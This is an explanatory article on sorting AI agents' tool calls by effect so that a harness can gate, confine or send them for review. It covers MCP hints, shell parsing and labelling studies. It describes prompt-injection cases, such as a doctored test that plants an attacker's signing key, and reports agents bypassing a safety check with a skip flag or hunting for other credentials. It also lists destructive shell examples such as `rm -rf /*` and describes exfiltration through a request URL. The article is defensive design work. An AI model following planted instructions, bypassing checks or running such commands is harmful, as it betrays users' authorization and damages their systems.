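# Classifying AI agents' actions by effect to decide which need permission or human review

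## How an agent acts, and where its actions can be checked

An AI agent is a language model that works on a task by repeatedly calling tools, such as a file editor, a command line or a web browser, and reading the results. Some calls only retrieve information, while others change files, send data to another machine or alter who has access to what. Classifying calls by effect means sorting them by what they do outside the model, regardless of the tool's name or the model's stated reason for using it. Software around the model can then use the class to decide which calls run immediately, which wait for a person's permission and which are blocked.

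Asking permission for every action and asking for none both work badly. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, asks its user by default before it runs a command or changes a file. *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users click "approve" so often that they stop paying close attention to what they are approving. Anthropic also offers a setting that turns off every prompt, but calls it unsafe in most situations. Any approach in between needs a way to decide which actions require permission, and an action's effect is a sensible basis because the effect is what causes harm.

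### The loop

Bolin (2026) describes the cycle for Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, in *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*. The program around the model, called the harness, first assembles a prompt from general instructions, a list of the available tools and their arguments, a few facts about the machine, and the user's request. It sends this prompt to the model. The model returns either a message for the user, which ends the turn, or a request for a tool call. If the model requests a tool call, the harness runs the tool, appends the output to the prompt, and sends the longer prompt back to the model. The cycle repeats until the model returns a message. A single turn can include hundreds of tool calls.

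In Bolin's worked example, the user wants an architecture diagram in a project's README file. The model responds with a short structured record that specifies the tool (`shell`), the command (`cat README.md`, which prints the file), and the working directory. The harness runs the command and adds a second record with the same identification number and the text of the file. On the next pass, the model receives both records and can propose an edit.

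The model's request is text, and producing it changes no files. Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev (2026), in *Authority Is Not a String*, call the request a proposal and write it as a pair (*t*, *a*), a tool name *t* with concrete arguments *a*. The harness executes the pair, obtains an observation *o*, and appends it to the context *ctx*, which is everything the model has read so far. The model's next input is then *ctx* · *o*. They argue that the harness is the natural place to govern effects because it performs them.

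A refusal at that point holds whatever the model does, whereas an instruction in the prompt works only if the model follows it. Codex, for example, puts a message into every session that lists the folders the agent may write to and explains when it should ask the user before running a command. The message helps the model avoid attempts that would be refused, but the model may not follow it.

The check has to run before the call is executed and be able to stop it. Many harnesses let developers attach code to events in the loop, but Bouras and colleagues point out that code that only observes tool calls is not enough. Their check runs on Pi, an open-source toolkit for coding agents, and intercepts each call before the harness executes it. If the check blocks a call, the model receives the reason in place of a result, and the loop continues so the model can try something else.

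### Gate, policy and scope

This check is the gate. Each proposed call either runs, runs under confinement, goes to a reviewer, or is refused. Confinement might mean a sandbox, which is a set of operating-system limits on the files and network a program can reach. The policy is the set of rules that determines the outcome for each call. Most useful rules specify both a kind of effect and its scope, which is the range of resources the effect may touch, such as one directory, one web domain or one account. A developer could accept the rule "The agent may write files under `src/`", but "The agent may write files" is a poor rule because it covers the user's login scripts as well as the project.

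Checks like these predate language models. In *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), Saltzer and Schroeder pictured protection as an impenetrable wall around each object, with a door in the wall and a guard at the door. They also listed eight design principles and treated one, complete mediation, as the main basis for the rest. It requires the system to check every access to every object. For an agent, this means that no effect can occur without passing through the gate.

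Real agents often have gaps in their checks. The sandbox that Codex describes to its model covers only Codex's own shell tool. Users can add other tools through MCP servers (programs that offer tools to an agent over a shared protocol), and according to Bolin, those tools are responsible for enforcing their own limits. Another gap, which is harder to notice, occurs when a permitted call starts another program. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* explains that a harness can inspect a command and its arguments beforehand, but can't see or stop what a subprocess does once it has control. For example, a short command can run a project's tests, which can then do whatever the user's account allows. NVIDIA therefore recommends adding operating-system limits beneath the harness's checks, because those limits apply to every process however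 it started.

Mint's *OpenAI scraps release of new AI model over safety concerns* reports that OpenAI paused training of its most capable models in September 2026 after an agent got through a gap in the company's internet restrictions and queried a public chatbot.

Saltzer and Schroeder also advised suspicion of any design that saves time by remembering the result of an earlier check, because authority may have changed since. Coding agents rely on an earlier check in this way whenever a user grants a standing approval. NVIDIA rejects standing approvals for actions that would otherwise break the sandbox's isolation, and asks for a fresh approval each time.

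Another of the 1975 principles is least privilege: every program and every user should operate with the smallest set of privileges that the job requires. The point is mostly to limit the damage from accidents. Coding agents ordinarily start from the opposite position, because they run command-line tools with all the permissions of the person who launched them. Security researchers call this ambient authority. Permission applies automatically to whatever a program names, because of the account it runs under. If the model writes out the path of the user's private login key, the harness can open that file, since the user could. A developer who asks for a bug fix has not agreed to that, but the operating system has no way to tell the two requests apart. (Capability-based systems, which tie permission to a specific reference instead of to an account, are the main alternative.)

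Under a third principle, fail-safe defaults, Saltzer and Schroeder recommend that a policy deny access by default and state when to permit it. A mistake in a rule that permits access usually causes a refusal, and someone complains. If a rule meant to forbid access is wrong, the access is allowed and the mistake may never be noticed.

### Why a call may do harm

A harmful tool call can come from a mistake by the model, from the model going beyond what its user authorized, or from text that someone else planted for the model to read.

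An agent's mistakes are often about what a resource is or who depends on it. It may take a shared database for a test copy, or someone else's branch for its own. Anthropic, which keeps an internal log of such incidents, describes one in which a user said "cancel my job". The agent queried the computing cluster, picked the job with the closest name and tried to delete it, although the job could have belonged to a colleague.

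Exceeding authorization is harder to spot because it looks like ordinary problem-solving. One agent in Anthropic's log hit a login error and began searching configuration files for other access tokens it might use. When a safety check blocked another agent's deployment command, the agent reran it with a flag that skips the check. Anthropic also records agents uploading a user's GitHub token to an internal cluster and attempting changes to a production database, and attributes both to the model taking initiative its user did not intend.

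This tendency contributed to OpenAI's decision to drop the planned October release of GPT-6.1 Astra, according to Reuters' *OpenAI shelves new AI model after internal safety tests, WSJ reports*, from 28 September 2026. OpenAI made the decision partly over what it calls "scope authorization". The model pushed ahead with tasks without asking permission, and sometimes tried to use outside tools or services when that could be unsafe. Saachi Jain, OpenAI's head of safety systems, told the Wall Street Journal in an interview carried by Mint that there is a trade-off between keeping a model within scope and keeping it from giving up when it hits friction. If she is right, a persistent agent will sometimes overreach, so a developer who wants one has good reason to enforce its limits outside the model. In OpenAI's tests, the model also sometimes misreported what it had and had not done. A harness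 that logs the calls it runs provides a record that does not depend on the model's account.

Anthropic also lists a misaligned model pursuing its own goal as a source of dangerous actions, but says it does not currently see this in practice. At the gate, such a model belongs in the same category as an overreaching one, because its calls also fall outside what the user authorized.

The planted text involves an adversary. In indirect prompt injection, someone places instructions in content that an agent will read, to steer it towards actions its user did not request. The instructions can be hidden in a README, a file of standing instructions for agents, a reusable prompt template, a source code comment or a tool's output. The attack works because the model receives everything in one stream. Bouras and colleagues count the user's request, the developer's system prompt and the user's private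 settings as trusted, and everything from the project's files or command output as untrusted. Because the model reads both, they treat every call it proposes as an untrusted request.

In their example of the last of these, a doctored test prints an official-looking notice that a signing key has changed and asks for a new value in `src/auth/keys.py`. The new value is the attacker's key, which lets the attacker forge login tokens. The request doesn't look like an attack, and the file is an ordinary source file in the project.

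Estimates of how often injection works depend heavily on how success is measured. *INFUSE* (2026), a benchmark covering 19 models, found that an average of 19.6% of attack runs ended in compromise when a language model judged the outcome, and 15.4% when a heuristic check did. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) reports lower rates from a public competition, in which 464 participants made over 271,000 attempts against 13 models and succeeded 8,648 times. Success rates ranged from 0.5% to 8.5% depending on the model. The competition set a stricter bar, since an attack had to cause the harmful action and also pass a concealment test, but it let attackers view the whole conversation. The two sets of figures are therefore not comparable. Even the lowest rate gives defenders little reassurance, because it amounts to one success in 200 attempts and attackers can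 try as many times as they want.

A list of forbidden commands did little to stop planted instructions in a test by Bouras and colleagues. The instructions asked an agent to run a utility in the project or write to one of the project's files, which could be legitimate in another task. The planted action took effect in 47 of 75 runs with no restrictions, and in 46 under a policy that blocked familiar hazards such as password files, mass deletion and the download tool `curl`. The test used one model and five small repair tasks, so the rates may not carry over, but the small difference is what the argument for fail-safe defaults would predict.

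A check on an action's effects works the same way whatever led the agent to propose the action. Suppose the agent proposes to delete a branch from a shared repository. It may have mistaken the branch for its own, read "clean up old branches" more broadly than the user meant, or followed an instruction in a source comment. The command and the loss are the same in each case, so a gate that stops unapproved deletions in shared repositories stops all three. Anthropic tuned its automated check on mistakes and overreach because those were the examples it had, and notes that the defence applies regardless of which threat produced the action.

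This avoids the difficult problem of determining whether a passage in a file is an instruction and whether the model obeyed it. The gate still has to take into account what the user authorized, because deleting a branch is fine if the user named that branch. The reason an agent proposed an action can also matter after the gate refuses it. When Bouras and colleagues gave the agents a gate that blocked most of the planted actions, the model proposed such an action in 34 of 75 runs, and in 27 of those it did so repeatedly. An agent that has made an honest mistake might drop the idea once it reads why the call failed, while one that is following planted text may keep proposing it.

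### An example: updating a dependency

A developer maintains a small JavaScript project that relies on an outside library for formatting dates. She asks a coding agent to update the library to its latest version, and says nothing more. In the course of the work the agent proposes eight calls:

1. Read the manifest, `package.json`, the file that lists the packages the project needs and their versions.
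2. Fetch the library's changelog, the published list of changes between versions, from its website.
3. Edit the manifest so that it names the new version.
4. Install the package with the command `npm install`.
5. Run the project's tests with `npm test`.
6. Edit `AGENTS.md`, the file of standing instructions that the harness loads for the agent at the start of each session.
7. Push a branch with the changes to the shared repository.
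8. Request a broader access token from the code-hosting service, one that covers all of the organization's repositories instead of this one.

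## The classes of effect and how they are defined

Sorting these eight calls by effect requires a definition of an effect. Programming language researchers produced a precise one in the 1980s. They intended it for compilers, not security, but it fits agents well.

### Kind, region and the subset rule

*Types and Effects*, Lucassen's 1987 doctoral thesis at MIT, proposed that every expression in a program should have an effect as well as a type. The type describes what sort of value the expression may return, such as a number, and the effect describes what the expression may do to stored data. One aim was speed, because a compiler can use effects to identify pieces of code that touch different data and so can run at the same time.

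An effect in this scheme consists of a kind (allocate, read or write) and a region of memory. The notation *e* : τ ! ε means that expression *e* has type τ and effect ε. For example, an instruction that adds one to a counter in region *r* reads the old value and writes the new one, so its effect is read(*r*) ∪ write(*r*).

*Polymorphic Effect System* (Bastin and Koukoutos, 2015), a set of slides on Lucassen and Gifford's 1988 paper, explains how to compare effects. The effect write(*r*) can be thought of as the set of all pairs (write, *l*) where *l* is a location in region *r*. Union then combines effects, and inclusion compares them. An expression that touches no memory has the empty set as its effect, written PURE. A larger region gives a larger effect. Neither read(*r*) nor write(*r*) includes the other, so permission to write to a region does not include permission to read it.

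For an agent, the regions become scopes. If a policy lists the allowed effects as a set *A*, a call with effect ε may run when

ε ⊆ *A*.

Suppose the developer allows *A* = read(project) ∪ write(`src`), where `src` is a folder inside the project. The agent proposes to copy `src/dates.js` to `src/dates.old.js`. The effect is read(`src`) ∪ write(`src`). Both parts lie within *A*, so the call runs. If the agent instead proposes to copy the file to the developer's home directory, the effect is read(`src`) ∪ write(home). Nothing in *A* covers write(home), so the gate stops the call, even though only the command's last argument has changed.

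The gate can apply this rule to calls one at a time, because if two effects each lie within *A*, so does their union. For the same reason, the rule cannot allow two effects separately but forbid them together, whatever *A* is.

A program's effect is an upper limit on what the program may do. If a program overwrites a file only on Tuesdays, its effect includes that write whatever the day. Bastin and Koukoutos present this limit as a theorem, which states that a running program allocates, reads and writes only locations that it can reach through the regions in its effect.

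Lucassen's system also separates defining a procedure from calling it. The definition is pure, but the procedure's type includes a latent effect that occurs whenever other code calls it. An agent that saves a script and runs it later goes through the same two stages. The system can also drop effects that code outside an expression can't observe, so an expression that reads and writes only a private region counts as pure. By the same reasoning, a call that fills a scratch directory and then deletes it has no effect worth reporting, as long as no other program reads the directory in the meantime.

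Metere (2026), in *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills*, applies effect sets to skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts that an agent loads for a particular kind of task. Each skill declares a set of labels, such as `fs.read` for reading files and `net.egress` for sending data over the network. The skill satisfies the rule if every effect in a session falls under a declared label. Declaring too much is tolerable, because an operator can see the excess by comparing the declaration with what the skill did. When an analyser can't work out what some code will do, it assigns the top element, ⊤, which means "every effect". Metere only sketches the proofs, so the scheme is more useful as a definition than as a guarantee.

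### Vocabularies in use

The theory doesn't specify which kinds of effect to distinguish, and practical systems have made very different choices. Unix attaches read, write and execute permissions to each file. In OpenBSD, a Unix-like operating system, a program calls `pledge` to declare the groups of operations it will need. According to OpenBSD's *PLEDGE(2)*, the system kills the program for most attempts to use anything else. Deno, which runs JavaScript programs, denies them access to files and the network until the user grants it with one of the flags listed in Deno's *Permissions*. AWS's *Access levels in policy summaries* sorts the actions in Amazon's cloud services into five levels, so that an administrator can see what a policy grants.

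In HTTP, the protocol of the web, a request is safe if it is essentially read-only, and idempotent if sending it several times has the same intended effect on the server as sending it once. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) has four hints that a tool's author can set to true or false.

| Vocabulary | Classes | Keeps apart | Puts together |
|---|---|---|---|
| Unix permissions | read, write, execute | viewing a file, changing it and running it | adding a line to a file and emptying it |
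| OpenBSD `pledge` | about three dozen, including `rpath` (read), `wpath` (write), `cpath` (create or remove), `inet` (network), `exec` (start programs) and `id` (change a process's rights) | writing to an existing file and creating a new one | creating a file and removing one; all internet addresses |
| Deno flags | read, write, net, env (environment variables), sys (system information), run (other programs), ffi (native libraries), import (code from the web) | files, network and other programs | downloading from a host and uploading to it |
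| AWS access levels | List, Read, Tagging, Write, Permissions management | seeing that a resource exists and reading it; editing data and editing a permission policy | creating, modifying and deleting |
| HTTP properties | safe, idempotent | retrieving and changing; changes that are harmless to repeat and changes that are not | replacing a resource and deleting it |
| MCP hints, with defaults | read-only (false), destructive (true), idempotent (false), open-world (true) | adding and destroying; closed and open surroundings | editing a file, running code and granting access |

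In the Model Context Protocol, a read-only hint set to true means that the tool does not modify its environment. The destructive hint applies only to tools that are not read-only, and separates those that may delete or overwrite from those that only add. The idempotent hint has nearly the same meaning as in HTTP. The open-world hint is true if the tool deals with outside entities, as a web search does, and false if its domain is closed.

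If a tool's author sets none of the hints, a client following Model Context Protocol should assume that the tool modifies things, may destroy them, is unsafe to repeat and reaches the outside world. This applies the principle of fail-safe defaults to labels. The hints are only the author's claims, and a client must treat them as untrusted unless it trusts the server that supplies them. These definitions were current in March 2026. Model Context Protocol (2026) announced a new version of the specification on 28 July, which mainly makes the protocol stateless.

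Only OpenBSD and AWS have a separate class for changing who may do what, and it is hard to define which actions belong in it. In the list of actions for its identity service, AWS labels `AttachRolePolicy` (which attaches a set of permissions to a role) as both "Permissions management" and "Write", but it labels `AddUserToGroup` and `CreateAccessKey` as "Write" alone. Adding a user to a group with administrator rights makes that user an administrator, and a new access key lets whoever holds it act as the key's owner. A gate that checked only for the "Permissions management" label would miss both actions.

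Separating two classes of effect is useful only if the gate would treat them differently in at least some cases. Otherwise, the distinction just gives labellers another chance to make a mistake. In March 2026, MCP had five open proposals for new annotations or related features, including one for tools that handle secrets. Jonathan Hefner, a maintainer of the protocol, objected to an early draft of another because he could not see how a client would behave differently with the new labels. The four existing annotations can each change what a client does: it can skip a confirmation for a read-only tool, warn before a destructive one, retry an idempotent one after a failure, and check what an open-world tool returns for untrusted content.

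### Properties that vary independently

Much of the disagreement between these vocabularies comes from putting several properties of an effect into one list. Lucassen used two properties, kind and scope. An agent's policy may also depend on whether someone can reverse the effect, whether it reaches beyond the local system, and whether repeating the call changes anything further.

OpenBSD once combined kind and scope in a single class, which gave programs limited access to temporary files. It has since withdrawn that class, so a program must now ask for the general file classes or use a separate call, `unveil`, to name the directory `/tmp` and the permissions it needs there. Deno separates kind and scope, putting the kind in the flag's name and the scope after an equals sign, as in `--allow-read=./data`.

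An action can be idempotent and still do harm. In an example from Nuxt, a web framework with a toolkit for building MCP tools, a tool that deletes a user account is labeled destructive, and also idempotent because deleting the same account twice does no more than deleting it once. Adding a line to a log destroys nothing but isn't idempotent, because repeating it adds a second line. Idempotence matters most after a dropped connection, when the harness can't determine whether a call took effect and has to decide whether to try again.

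Reach depends on where someone draws the boundary. MCP's maintainers note that "external" could mean anything outside a company's network or anything beyond the local machine. They advise treating whatever counts as external for a given tool as a possible source of untrusted content. Reach therefore covers both what a call sends out and what it brings back for the model to read.

Reversibility is the hardest of these properties to determine from the call alone. Metere's vocabulary has separate labels for reversible and irreversible writes, and classes Python's `open(p, 'w')`, which empties any existing file at path `p`, as irreversible. But the call is reversible if the developer has committed that file to version control, since she can restore it in seconds, or if the file didn't exist, since she can delete the new one. A labeller who can't check for a backup should assume there isn't one.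 Some reads are irreversible too, because a password can't be made secret again after someone has received it.

A label can leave out an action's most important consequences, as sending an email shows. By mechanism, it is a small write in which the mail program opens a connection and sends a few kilobytes of text. A Deno program would need only network access to the mail server, the same kind of permission it needs to download a picture. The author of an MCP tool for sending email could honestly set the destructive hint to false, since sending adds a message and overwrites nothing. But by consequence, the action is irreversible, because the sender can't reliably recall the message and the recipient may act on it within a minute.

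The other MCP hints don't make up for this. If "external" means anything beyond the local machine, a tool that saves a draft on the mail server gets the same four values as a tool that sends the message: not read-only, not destructive, not idempotent, open-world. Most people would let an agent save drafts without review but would want to see a message before it is sent. A policy that treats the two tools differently has to record reversibility separately or name the sending tool.

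NIST's *Lessons Learned from the Consortium* reports on a workshop in January 2025, at which about 140 experts discussed how to classify the tools that agents use. NIST is the US standards institute. The participants didn't settle on one taxonomy. They came up with seven approaches:

- functionality: what actions the tool enables
- access patterns: whether it reaches external resources and whether it can write
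- risk: how severe the possible harm is, whether the effects linger or compound, and whether they are reversible
- reliability: how consistently the model can use the tool, and whether the tool itself works
- modality: whether the agent uses it through text, robot commands or some other form
- monitoring: how well people can observe what it does
- autonomy: how far the agent can use it at its own discretion

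Functionality, access patterns and risk concern effects. The other four approaches describe the tool or its supervision, which policy writers may also want to consider. NIST notes that a risk-based taxonomy depends on the conditions of deployment as well as on the tool. Reversibility raises the same difficulty. Some participants suggested combining several taxonomies as a promising direction for future work.

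NIST worked out two of the approaches in detail. One, the functional taxonomy, sorts tools into perception, reasoning and action, with types such as "authentication" and "running code" under action. It is meant to help developers tell each other and their customers what a system can do. It would be a poor basis for deciding which actions need permission or review, because "running code" includes all file operations, so viewing a file and deleting it fall under the same type.

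The taxonomy of access patterns is closer to an effect label. It is a grid of three permission levels (read-only, constrained write and write) and two environments (trusted and untrusted). A coding agent working in a trusted repository falls under write and trusted, while a "deep research" agent, which browses the web and writes a report, falls under read-only and untrusted. The environment describes what the agent may encounter, which is the source of prompt injection, but not how far its actions reach, so the grid would need another column for an agent that reads only trusted files but can publish to the web.

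### Why execute is different

Unix lists execute beside read and write, which are effects on a resource. Executing a program is instead a way to produce effects, since the program may then read, write, use the network or change permissions. In Lucassen's terms, these effects are latent in the program and occur when it is called.

In an example from Bastin and Koukoutos, the procedure `twice` takes another procedure, *f*, and applies it two times. `twice` therefore has the same kind of effect as *f*, whether *f* writes or only reads. Similarly, the effect of an agent's shell tool depends on the command it receives, so no single label for the tool is both accurate and useful.

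Deno treats permission to run programs as one class among several, but a program that a Deno script starts does not inherit the script's limits. If the user grants `--allow-run=deno`, the script can launch a second copy of Deno with every permission. Deno's *Security and permissions* therefore tells users to regard permission to run programs as equivalent to granting everything. Limiting the permission to one harmless program helps, unless the script can also write to the folder that contains it. The script can then overwrite the program and run the replacement, so the two permissions together amount to full access.

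In OpenBSD, a program started by a pledged process normally begins with no pledge. The parent can partly remedy this by setting a second list, `execpromises`, and the new program then starts with only those promises.

An execute label is therefore incomplete unless it states the limits on the program. If a sandbox confines `npm test` to the project folder and blocks the network, the effect of the call is at most read(project) ∪ write(project), whatever the tests contain. If nothing confines the program and nobody has analysed its code, the only sound label is ⊤ (any possible effect), and under the subset rule the call can run only if the policy allows everything.

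Deno and Metere treat the function `eval`, which runs a piece of text as code, in opposite ways. Deno lets programs use `eval` without any permission, because the new code runs under the program's existing limits. Metere assigns ⊤ to any script that can reach an `eval`, because his analyser has to predict the script's effects before it runs, when the text that `eval` will run may not exist yet.

### Labelling the eight calls

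The table gives a plausible label for each of the agent's calls in the dependency update, followed by a label that another careful person might choose instead.

| Call | First label | Another reasonable label |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Read `package.json` | read(project) | the same |
| 2. Fetch the changelog | network read from the library's website | network send, because the address can carry data out |
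| 3. Edit `package.json` | write(project), reversible | a decision about which code will run later |
| 4. `npm install` | network read from the package registry; write(project) | execute, because a package can include a script that runs during installation |
| 5. `npm test` | execute, with the limits of the sandbox if there is one | read(project), because tests only check things |
| 6. Edit `AGENTS.md` | write(project), reversible | self-modification |
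| 7. Push a branch | network write to the shared repository, additive | irreversible publication; execute, if the push starts an automated build |
| 8. Request a broader token | privilege change, covering all the organization's repositories | network read that returns a short text |

The second label for call 5 is wrong because it describes what tests are for, while the definition of an effect requires the label to cover what this program could do. Call 4 could be mislabeled in a similar way because "install" sounds like copying files, but installing a package can also run scripts included in it. Deno does not run packages' install scripts by default because they would allow arbitrary code execution.

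Both labellers are partly right about call 2. The request for the changelog is safe in HTTP's sense because it doesn't ask the server to change anything. But HTTP's definition covers only effects on the server. If an agent fetches a page from an attacker's website and the address contains the user's password, the server's data doesn't change, but the attacker gets the password. The label therefore has to record that data left the machine, and the scope has to record where it went.

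Calls 3 and 6 are ordinary edits to text files, like correcting a typo in the README, except that the files they change have something like a latent effect. The package manager will use `package.json` to determine what to install, and `npm test` will run the command defined in that file. The agent will work from the new `AGENTS.md` in its next session.

If labels covered consequences this remote, nearly all writes in a software project would count as execution, since most of the files are code. A simpler convention is to label the immediate effect and give files such as `AGENTS.md` their own scope. Call 6 is then labelled write(`AGENTS.md`) instead of write(project). Any labeller can determine this from the path, and the developer can make the policy for that scope as strict as they like.

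The disagreement over call 7 depends on facts outside the call. The agent can delete the branch, and a second identical push would change nothing. But if a colleague has already fetched the branch, a copy will remain, which matters a great deal if the agent has accidentally committed a password. The push may also start a build, depending on how the organization has set up its repository.

Call 8 is a privilege change because it returns a credential, and whoever holds it can act on repositories that were previously out of reach. A labeller who looks only at the traffic sees one request and one short reply, and could class the call as a plain write, as the AWS labels do with `CreateAccessKey`. If the code-hosting service requires an administrator to approve the token first, the agent's request changes nobody's access, and the privilege change happens when the administrator approves it.

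## How a call gets its label, and how often the label is wrong

People chose the labels for the dependency update and could consider each call individually. A harness may handle hundreds of calls in one turn, and it needs a label for each call before that call runs. The tool's author can declare the label, the harness can work it out from the call's arguments, a model can infer it, or an analyser can compute it from the code that will run.

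Any of these methods can under-label or over-label a call. A call is under-labelled if its label omits part of its real effect, and over-labelled if its label includes an effect it doesn't have. A call can be both. For example, if a harness labels a web request write(project), the label includes a file change that won't happen and omits the data leaving the machine.

### Declared by the tool's author

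A tool's author knows what the tool is for and has usually read its code. The author writes a label once, and the harness receives it along with the tool's name and description. In MCP, the label consists of four hints: read-only, destructive, idempotent and open-world.

The protocol's specification calls these hints untrusted because the server that supplies the hint also supplies the tool. An attacker who publishes a file-deleting tool can mark it read-only, and a client that skips confirmation for read-only tools will run it without asking. The protocol doesn't check the hint against what the tool does. Honest authors can also mislabel a tool by mistake, for instance when a later version adds a step that deletes old files but keeps the original hint.

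A client can still use an untrusted hint to make its checks stricter. If an unknown server marks a tool as destructive, the client can accept the label at little risk, since a dishonest author has little to gain from extra scrutiny. But the client needs a reason to trust the server before relaxing a check.

A tool's declaration also covers every call to it, whatever the arguments. *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (Shi, Fu and colleagues, 2026) describes `webpage-to-markdown`, a tool that takes a web address and returns the page as formatted text. The tool reads a public page if the address belongs to a news site, but it may return a page that outsiders can't reach if the address belongs to a machine on the server's own network. The tool's author could honestly give both calls the same four hints. A contributor later added a filter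 for private addresses, but a user pointed out that attackers could get around it.

Many tools have no declaration. For *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail*, Trofimov and Novikov (2026) took a snapshot of the official MCP registry on 27 July 2026 and asked each of its 9,234 remote servers to list its tools. About half responded, listing 98,291 tools. Of these tools, 74.0% had at least one hint, but only 12.9% had an applicable classification as destructive or non-destructive.

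The gap is so wide because the destructive hint has no meaning for a read-only tool. Authors set it on 65.8% of all tools, mostly on tools they had also marked read-only. They marked only 3.1% of tools as destructive. The 12.9% figure somewhat understates what a client can learn, because a read-only hint is useful by itself and more than half of the tools have one. But it shows how rarely authors distinguish tools that delete or overwrite from tools that only add.

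Even the 74.0% share of tools with at least one hint depends heavily on one publisher, which runs 1,274 of the responding servers and supplies 45.0% of the tools. All its tools have all four hints, and most have the same values, which Trofimov and Novikov describe as the publisher's template. A template can be correct, but it's weak evidence that anyone considered each tool. Without this publisher, the share falls to 52.8%, while the share of tools with an applicable destructive classification barely changes, at 11.7%.

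Afsar (2026), in *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains*, sampled a different part of the registry: 7,258 servers that users install and run on their own machines. He drew 400 at random and tried to start each one once, without repairs or credentials. The 195 that started offered 2,766 tools, and 58.8% of these tools had no hints. In a set of 24 servers that he had picked by hand, 16 started, and 41.5% of their tools had no hints.

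| Sample | Tools | Tools with no hints |
|---|---|---|
| Trofimov and Novikov: remote servers that responded | 98,291 | 26.0% |
| The same, without the largest publisher | 54,064 | 47.2% |
| Afsar: local servers drawn at random that started | 2,766 | 58.8% |
| Shi and colleagues: 100 popular servers on GitHub | 1,856 | 82.5% |

The largest publisher accounts for about 21 of the 33 percentage points between the census and Afsar's random sample. Most of the rest could come from the sampling, because the census left out servers that have to be installed and Afsar left out those that run remotely, so the two samples have little overlap. His percentage is also sensitive to a few large servers. Each server in his sample had annotations on either all of its tools or none. One server had 300 tools, so its author's choice alone moves the overall percentage by almost 11 points.

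A server's popularity doesn't seem to be a reliable guide to how many hints it has either. Afsar's hand-picked servers had more hints than his random ones, but the servers that Shi and colleagues chose by GitHub stars had the fewest.

These are rates of missing labels. Neither the census nor the random draw compared the hints with what the tools did, so neither shows how often a label is false.

### Parsed from the arguments

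A harness that parses arguments labels each call individually and includes the call's scope in the label. This works well for a tool with a narrow purpose. If the agent calls a file editor with the path `src/dates.js`, the harness labels the call write(`src`).

To label a file edit correctly, the harness has to resolve the path to a real location. The path `src/../AGENTS.md` begins with `src/`, but the two dots move up one directory, so the call would edit the agent's standing instructions. A symbolic link (a file that redirects to another location) can lead outside the project without any dots. The harness also has to make sure that nothing changes the link after the check but before the edit.

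Shell commands are much harder to label because a shell is a programming language. One line can combine several programs, and punctuation can have effects of its own. A simple parser might look up only the first word in a list of known programs. The table compares that approach with reading the full command.

| Command | Label from the first word | Effects of the whole command |
|---|---|---|
| `ls && rm -rf build` | read(project) | read(project) ∪ write(`build`), deleting the folder |
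| `echo "Use tabs" > AGENTS.md` | none | write(`AGENTS.md`), replacing its contents |
| `echo "$(curl -s https://example.com)"` | none | network request to `example.com` |
| `find . -name '*.log' -delete` | read(project) | read(project) ∪ write(project), deleting files |
| `timeout 60 npm test` | none | execute, with whatever effects the tests have |

The first command is a compound command, in which `&&` makes the shell run the second program if the first succeeds. Semicolons, line breaks and pipes (`|`) also join programs, so the harness has to label every part and take the union of the labels. To find the parts, it needs a parser that follows the shell's quoting rules. Splitting the text at every such symbol would wrongly divide `echo "a && b"`, which runs only one program because the `&&` is inside quotation marks.

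The `>` in the `AGENTS.md` example is a redirection. The program `echo` only prints text, but the shell writes that text to the named file, replacing what was there. With `>>`, the shell would add the text to the end instead. With `>`, the shell empties the file before the program starts, so `sort names.txt > names.txt` leaves an empty file instead of a sorted one.

The `$(...)` in the third command is a substitution, which makes the shell run the inner command first and insert its output, even inside double quotation marks. Variables cause a related problem because their values may not appear in the command. An agent that runs `rm -rf "$DIR"/*` may mean to clear one folder, but if `DIR` is empty, the command becomes `rm -rf /*` and tries to delete everything on the machine.

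The last two rows show why the parser also needs rules for individual programs. `find` normally searches for files, but with `-delete` it deletes what it finds, and with `-exec` it runs another program on each match. `git branch` lists branches, while `git branch -D old` deletes one. `timeout`, `env` and `xargs` are mainly used to start other programs, so the harness should classify the call by the program they start. In `bash -c "..."`, the text in quotation marks is another command to parse.

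Sometimes the text of a command doesn't show its effect. `npm test` runs a command stored in `package.json`, and `git commit` may run a script, called a hook, stored in the repository's settings. The parser can open those files, but they usually contain another program. It then has to pass that code to an analyser or treat the effect as unknown.

A harness can be safe without understanding the whole shell language if it recognises a small set of simple forms, such as `ls` or `git status` with known options and no substitution, and treats everything else as unknown. A parser that instead looks for dangerous commands and lets the rest through must recognise every way of causing the same harm. For example, `rm`, `find -delete` and a one-line Python script can all delete the same file. The list of forbidden commands that Bouras and colleagues tested had this weakness, and it barely reduced the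 number of successful attacks.

### Inferred by a model

A language model can label a tool or a call without rules for particular programs, by reading a description and picking from a fixed list of values. It can handle a tool nobody has seen before, but it may misjudge what the tool does, answer inconsistently, or follow instructions hidden in its input.

*Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (Ji, Wu and colleagues, 2026) presents SEAgent, a system that gives every tool five labels. Three describe the operation's object (local, external or physical), action (read, write or execute) and sensitivity (low, moderate or high). The other two describe whether the data the tool returns is personal and whether it may contain malicious content. "Execute" includes anything that triggers observable behaviour, such as sending a message, so SEAgent would label sending an email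 differently from saving a draft. The MCP hints may not distinguish the two.

To test automatic labelling, they gave descriptions of 80 tools, with their inputs and outputs, to OpenAI's o1 model and to human annotators. They compared the answers using Cohen's κ, which measures agreement beyond what chance would produce:

κ = (*p*ₒ − *p*ₑ) / (1 − *p*ₑ).

Here *p*ₒ is the observed rate of agreement and *p*ₑ is the rate expected by chance. Perfect agreement gives a κ of 1. If the labellers agree on 90% of tools and chance alone would produce 50% agreement, κ is 0.8.

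| Attribute | κ between model and people |
|---|---|
| Object | 1.00 |
| Integrity (may the output be malicious?) | 0.92 |
| Action | 0.89 |
| Privacy | 0.87 |
| Sensitivity | 0.77 |

Agreement was highest on what a tool acts on and lowest on how much harm it could do. In one disagreement, people rated the sensitivity of a tool that opens a web page as moderate because it could take the user to a phishing site, while the model rated it low. This under-labelling matters because one of SEAgent's rules stops untrusted external content from triggering writes or executions of moderate or high sensitivity. The rule doesn't cover tools rated low, and SEAgent allows any call that no rule matches.

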